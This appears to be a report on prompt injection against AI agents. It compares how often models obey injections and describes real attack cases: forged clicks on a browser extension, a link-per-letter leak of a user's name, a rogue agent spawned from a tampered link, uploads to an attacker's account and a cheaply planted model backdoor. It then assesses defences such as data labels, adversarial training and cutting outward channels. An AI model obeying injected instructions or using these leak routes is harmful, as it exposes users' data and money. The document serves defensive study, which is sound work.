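In Mellafe Zuvic's test of 27 models, cheaper models were much more likely to follow injections that presented a dangerous action as necessary for the user's task. The 12 cheaper models attempted the unauthorised call at a mean rate of 0.603, against 0.189 for the 15 flagship models. Gemini 3.1 Pro made no unauthorised attempts, while the cheaper Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite made them 98% of the time. Both groups had high outliers, however, so price alone doesn't reliably predict how well a model resists injection. All attempts took place in a sandbox, so the rates don't measure actual breaches. One person wrote the scenarios, each lasted a single turn, and the group averages have no confidence intervals.

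In separate paired tests, models were much more likely to obey an injection worded so that it appeared to serve the task. Gemma 3 12B never obeyed a crude injection but obeyed 57% of those that appeared to serve the task. For GLM-4.7, the rate rose from 28% to 100%. A false invoice appears to serve the task because the assistant's task is to pay invoices. A company that handles thousands of emails a day also has a financial reason to use a cheap model.

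### Why a low rate still matters

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

| Chance per attempt | 200 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| 0.05% | 10% | 39% |
| 0.41% | 56% | 98% |
| 2.09% | 99% | Almost 100% |

Real attempts aren't independent. An email that fails once will probably fail again, so resending it is less likely to work than the table suggests. But an attacker who learns from failures and rewrites the email can do better. The attacker can also try many targets. If 10,000 companies ran similar agents, one email to each would succeed against about 41 of them at a success rate of 0.41%.

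Blocking a sender after a few suspicious emails doesn't prevent prompt injection, because the attacker can practise elsewhere. Zhang, Zhao and colleagues trained their email writer against a copy of a typical agent, without feedback from the victim's agent. GPT-Red likewise refined its attack in a simulation before using it on the real vending machine.

Willison argues that in security "99% is a failing grade", because attackers will look for the remaining 1%. This is right if a single successful attack is catastrophic. If a daily cap keeps the loss tolerable, a low attack success rate is still useful because it makes that loss less frequent.

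### Which layers would have applied

In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) counted four attacks on AI agents by four research teams in about ten days of July 2026, including memory poisoning and an attack on Claude for Chrome. This browser extension runs any of nine built-in tasks, such as reading the user's Gmail, when the user clicks. The firm Manifold Security found that the extension didn't check whether the click was real, so another extension could forge one with six lines of code.

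In May, Anthropic had restricted outside callers to the fixed tasks. Malwarebytes' *Claude for Chrome flaw could let rogue extensions access your Gmail* points out that this limited which tasks a caller could request but didn't verify the caller's identity. In the default mode, the user still had to approve the task. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the task ran without the user's approval in "Act without asking" mode and that there was no fix as of 14 July.

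Parsing would not have helped, because the forged request appeared to come from the user. A manifest would have allowed the extension to read mail, because that was one of its normal functions. Exact approval could have stopped the attack if the user had noticed that they never asked for the task, and egress limits could have reduced the data that left the browser. The proper fix is to verify that the click came from the user.

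Another July attack got past an egress limit. Claude's chat assistant could fetch only addresses typed by the user, returned by a search, or found on pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul built a site that posed as a security check and told Claude to spell out the user's name by following one link per letter. Willison reports that this revealed the user's name, home city and employer.

The attacker had supplied the list of permitted choices. With 26 links on a page, each fetch can leak about 4.7 bits. A limit on fetches per site would have reduced the leak, but a short name could still have leaked. Anthropic instead stopped the tool from following links on pages it had fetched, which closed the route but also removed a useful function.

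AgentForger, an attack by the security firm Zenity, began with a tampered link to ChatGPT's agent builder. According to The Decoder's *One tampered ChatGPT link could spawn a rogue AI agent*, the builder ran a prompt contained in the link, in the victim's logged-in session. The new agent could read private data through the victim's connected services and received instructions from the attacker every five minutes. Requiring approval for sensitive actions should have stopped the attack, but the same prompt could turn that requirement off. Mellafe Zuvic's rule that nothing the model writes may change the policy covers this case.

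### Containing the damage

One approach is to accept that models will sometimes obey an attacker and to use software to limit the consequences. The best argument for this approach is that such limits don't depend on why the model misbehaves. ThreatCluster (2026) reports that Katie Paxton-Fear planted a backdoor in an openly available model for under $100, using ten malicious training examples. An email parser would have no effect on instructions built into the model. But as Mellafe Zuvic points out, a per-call check blocks an unlisted account whether the model's behaviour comes from an email or from its training.

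The weakness of this position is that an injected prompt can still cause a false summary, a biased recommendation or a harmful action that the agent is permitted to take. A company can accept these risks more easily when a mistake costs a few hundred pounds than when a doctor relies on the summary.

### Tracking data with labels

*Information-flow control* attaches labels to data and checks them before the data can affect an action or leave. CaMeL's interpreter records each value's sources and permitted readers. When the program combines two values, *x* and *y*, the labels of the result are

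sources = sources(*x*) ∪ sources(*y*)

readers = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

so the result keeps every source, and only people who may read both values may read it. If the accounts assistant combined the supplier list with a stranger's email, the resulting reply would still carry the list's restriction to company staff, and the runtime would refuse to send it outside. A payment rule could also require that the account number come only from company records.

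FIDES, from researchers at Microsoft, uses similar labels for an agent that chooses each tool call as it goes. Once the model has read untrusted text, FIDES treats whatever the model writes as untrusted too. To avoid this, the runtime can store a tool's result in a variable, which the model can pass to another tool without reading its contents.

Labels are useful because they don't depend on the attacker's wording. Even a persuasive email can't change the record of where an account number came from. How much utility an agent loses depends on how strictly the rules treat untrusted data. On AgentDojo, CaMeL completed 77% of tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, whereas PACE lost most of its utility there when it relied on provenance alone.

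SARA tries to reduce that drawback by letting untrusted data fill in a task but not extend it. For example, the agent may take a file's identifier from a search result, but not an extra recipient for the file. SARA also records which content first suggested an action, so an attacker's address doesn't become trusted just because it appears again. Its judgements about meaning may be wrong, so it lacks the certainty of fixed rules. An inflated bill from a genuine supplier would also carry all the right labels, because labels can't detect a lie from a permitted source.

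### Training models to resist

Training is the only one of these approaches that could prevent a false summary or a biased recommendation when the agent has to read free text. OpenAI trained GPT-Red, an attacking model, against several defending models at once. GPT-Red earned a reward for a successful attack, and the defenders earned one for resisting and finishing their original task. Without the requirement to finish the task, a defender could earn the reward by refusing to do anything.

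OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6. On OpenAI's hardest test of direct prompt injection, GPT-5.6 Sol failed one-sixth as often as the company's best model from four months earlier, and OpenAI found no loss of general ability. If these results hold in real use, this training is a much better trade-off than a sanitiser that deletes parts of legitimate invoices.

The success of an attack also depends heavily on the attacker. In a separate set of scenarios, human testers beat GPT-5.1 in 13% and GPT-Red, a trained attacker, beat it in 84%, so human testing alone understated the model's vulnerability. GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of 0.05% was measured against the system that helped train it. OpenAI reports that it keeps finding new attacks as it scales up this training, and criminals or other laboratories could train their own attackers.

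### Separating the three conditions

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warns against combining private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside world. Anyone who can place text in front of an agent with all three may be able to steal the data. Removing any one of them prevents this theft, even if the model obeys every injection. Willison considers outward communication the easiest to remove without making the agent much less useful.

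OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, released in June 2026, uses fixed rules to limit outgoing network requests. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, describes it as a tool for people at higher risk rather than for everyone, because it removes some functions.

Removing a condition completely can be difficult. Anthropic's Claude Cowork limited traffic to a list of hosts, but the list included Anthropic's developer service. Researchers at Prompt Armor got the agent to upload files there with the attacker's access key, which put the files in the attacker's account.

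The accounts assistant meets all three conditions because it reads supplier records, reads strangers' emails and sends replies. Limiting it to the eight standard replies nearly removes the third condition. However, the rule concerns data theft, and a false invoice can cause a payment without any private data leaving the company. Companies therefore need a similar rule for tools that spend money or change records.

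### Is a full fix possible?

David C, writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, says engineers can reduce the risk of prompt injection but not remove it. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body for AI developers, lists defence against prompt injection and memory poisoning among developers' ongoing work.

OpenAI presents prompt injection as a continuing contest with attackers. Its *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a programme to find and patch attacks on its browser agent before criminals use them. In July 2026, the company said it would keep using human testers, layered safeguards and monitoring alongside GPT-Red. On its help page for Lockdown Mode, OpenAI warns that injected text can still affect the accuracy of an answer.

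Some Anthropic staff are more optimistic. Cat Wu, who works on Claude Code, said the team had "pretty much mitigated every attack", and a colleague, Thariq Shihipar, suggested that the post announcing the 720 failed attempts should have claimed to defeat the lethal trifecta. Willison would like more independent confirmation. One untested attack uses a software package whose instructions tell the agent to download model files before running the tests. If the download program is malicious, the agent can give away everything it has access to by following what looks like an ordinary setup step. Willison doubts that any version of auto mode could prevent this.
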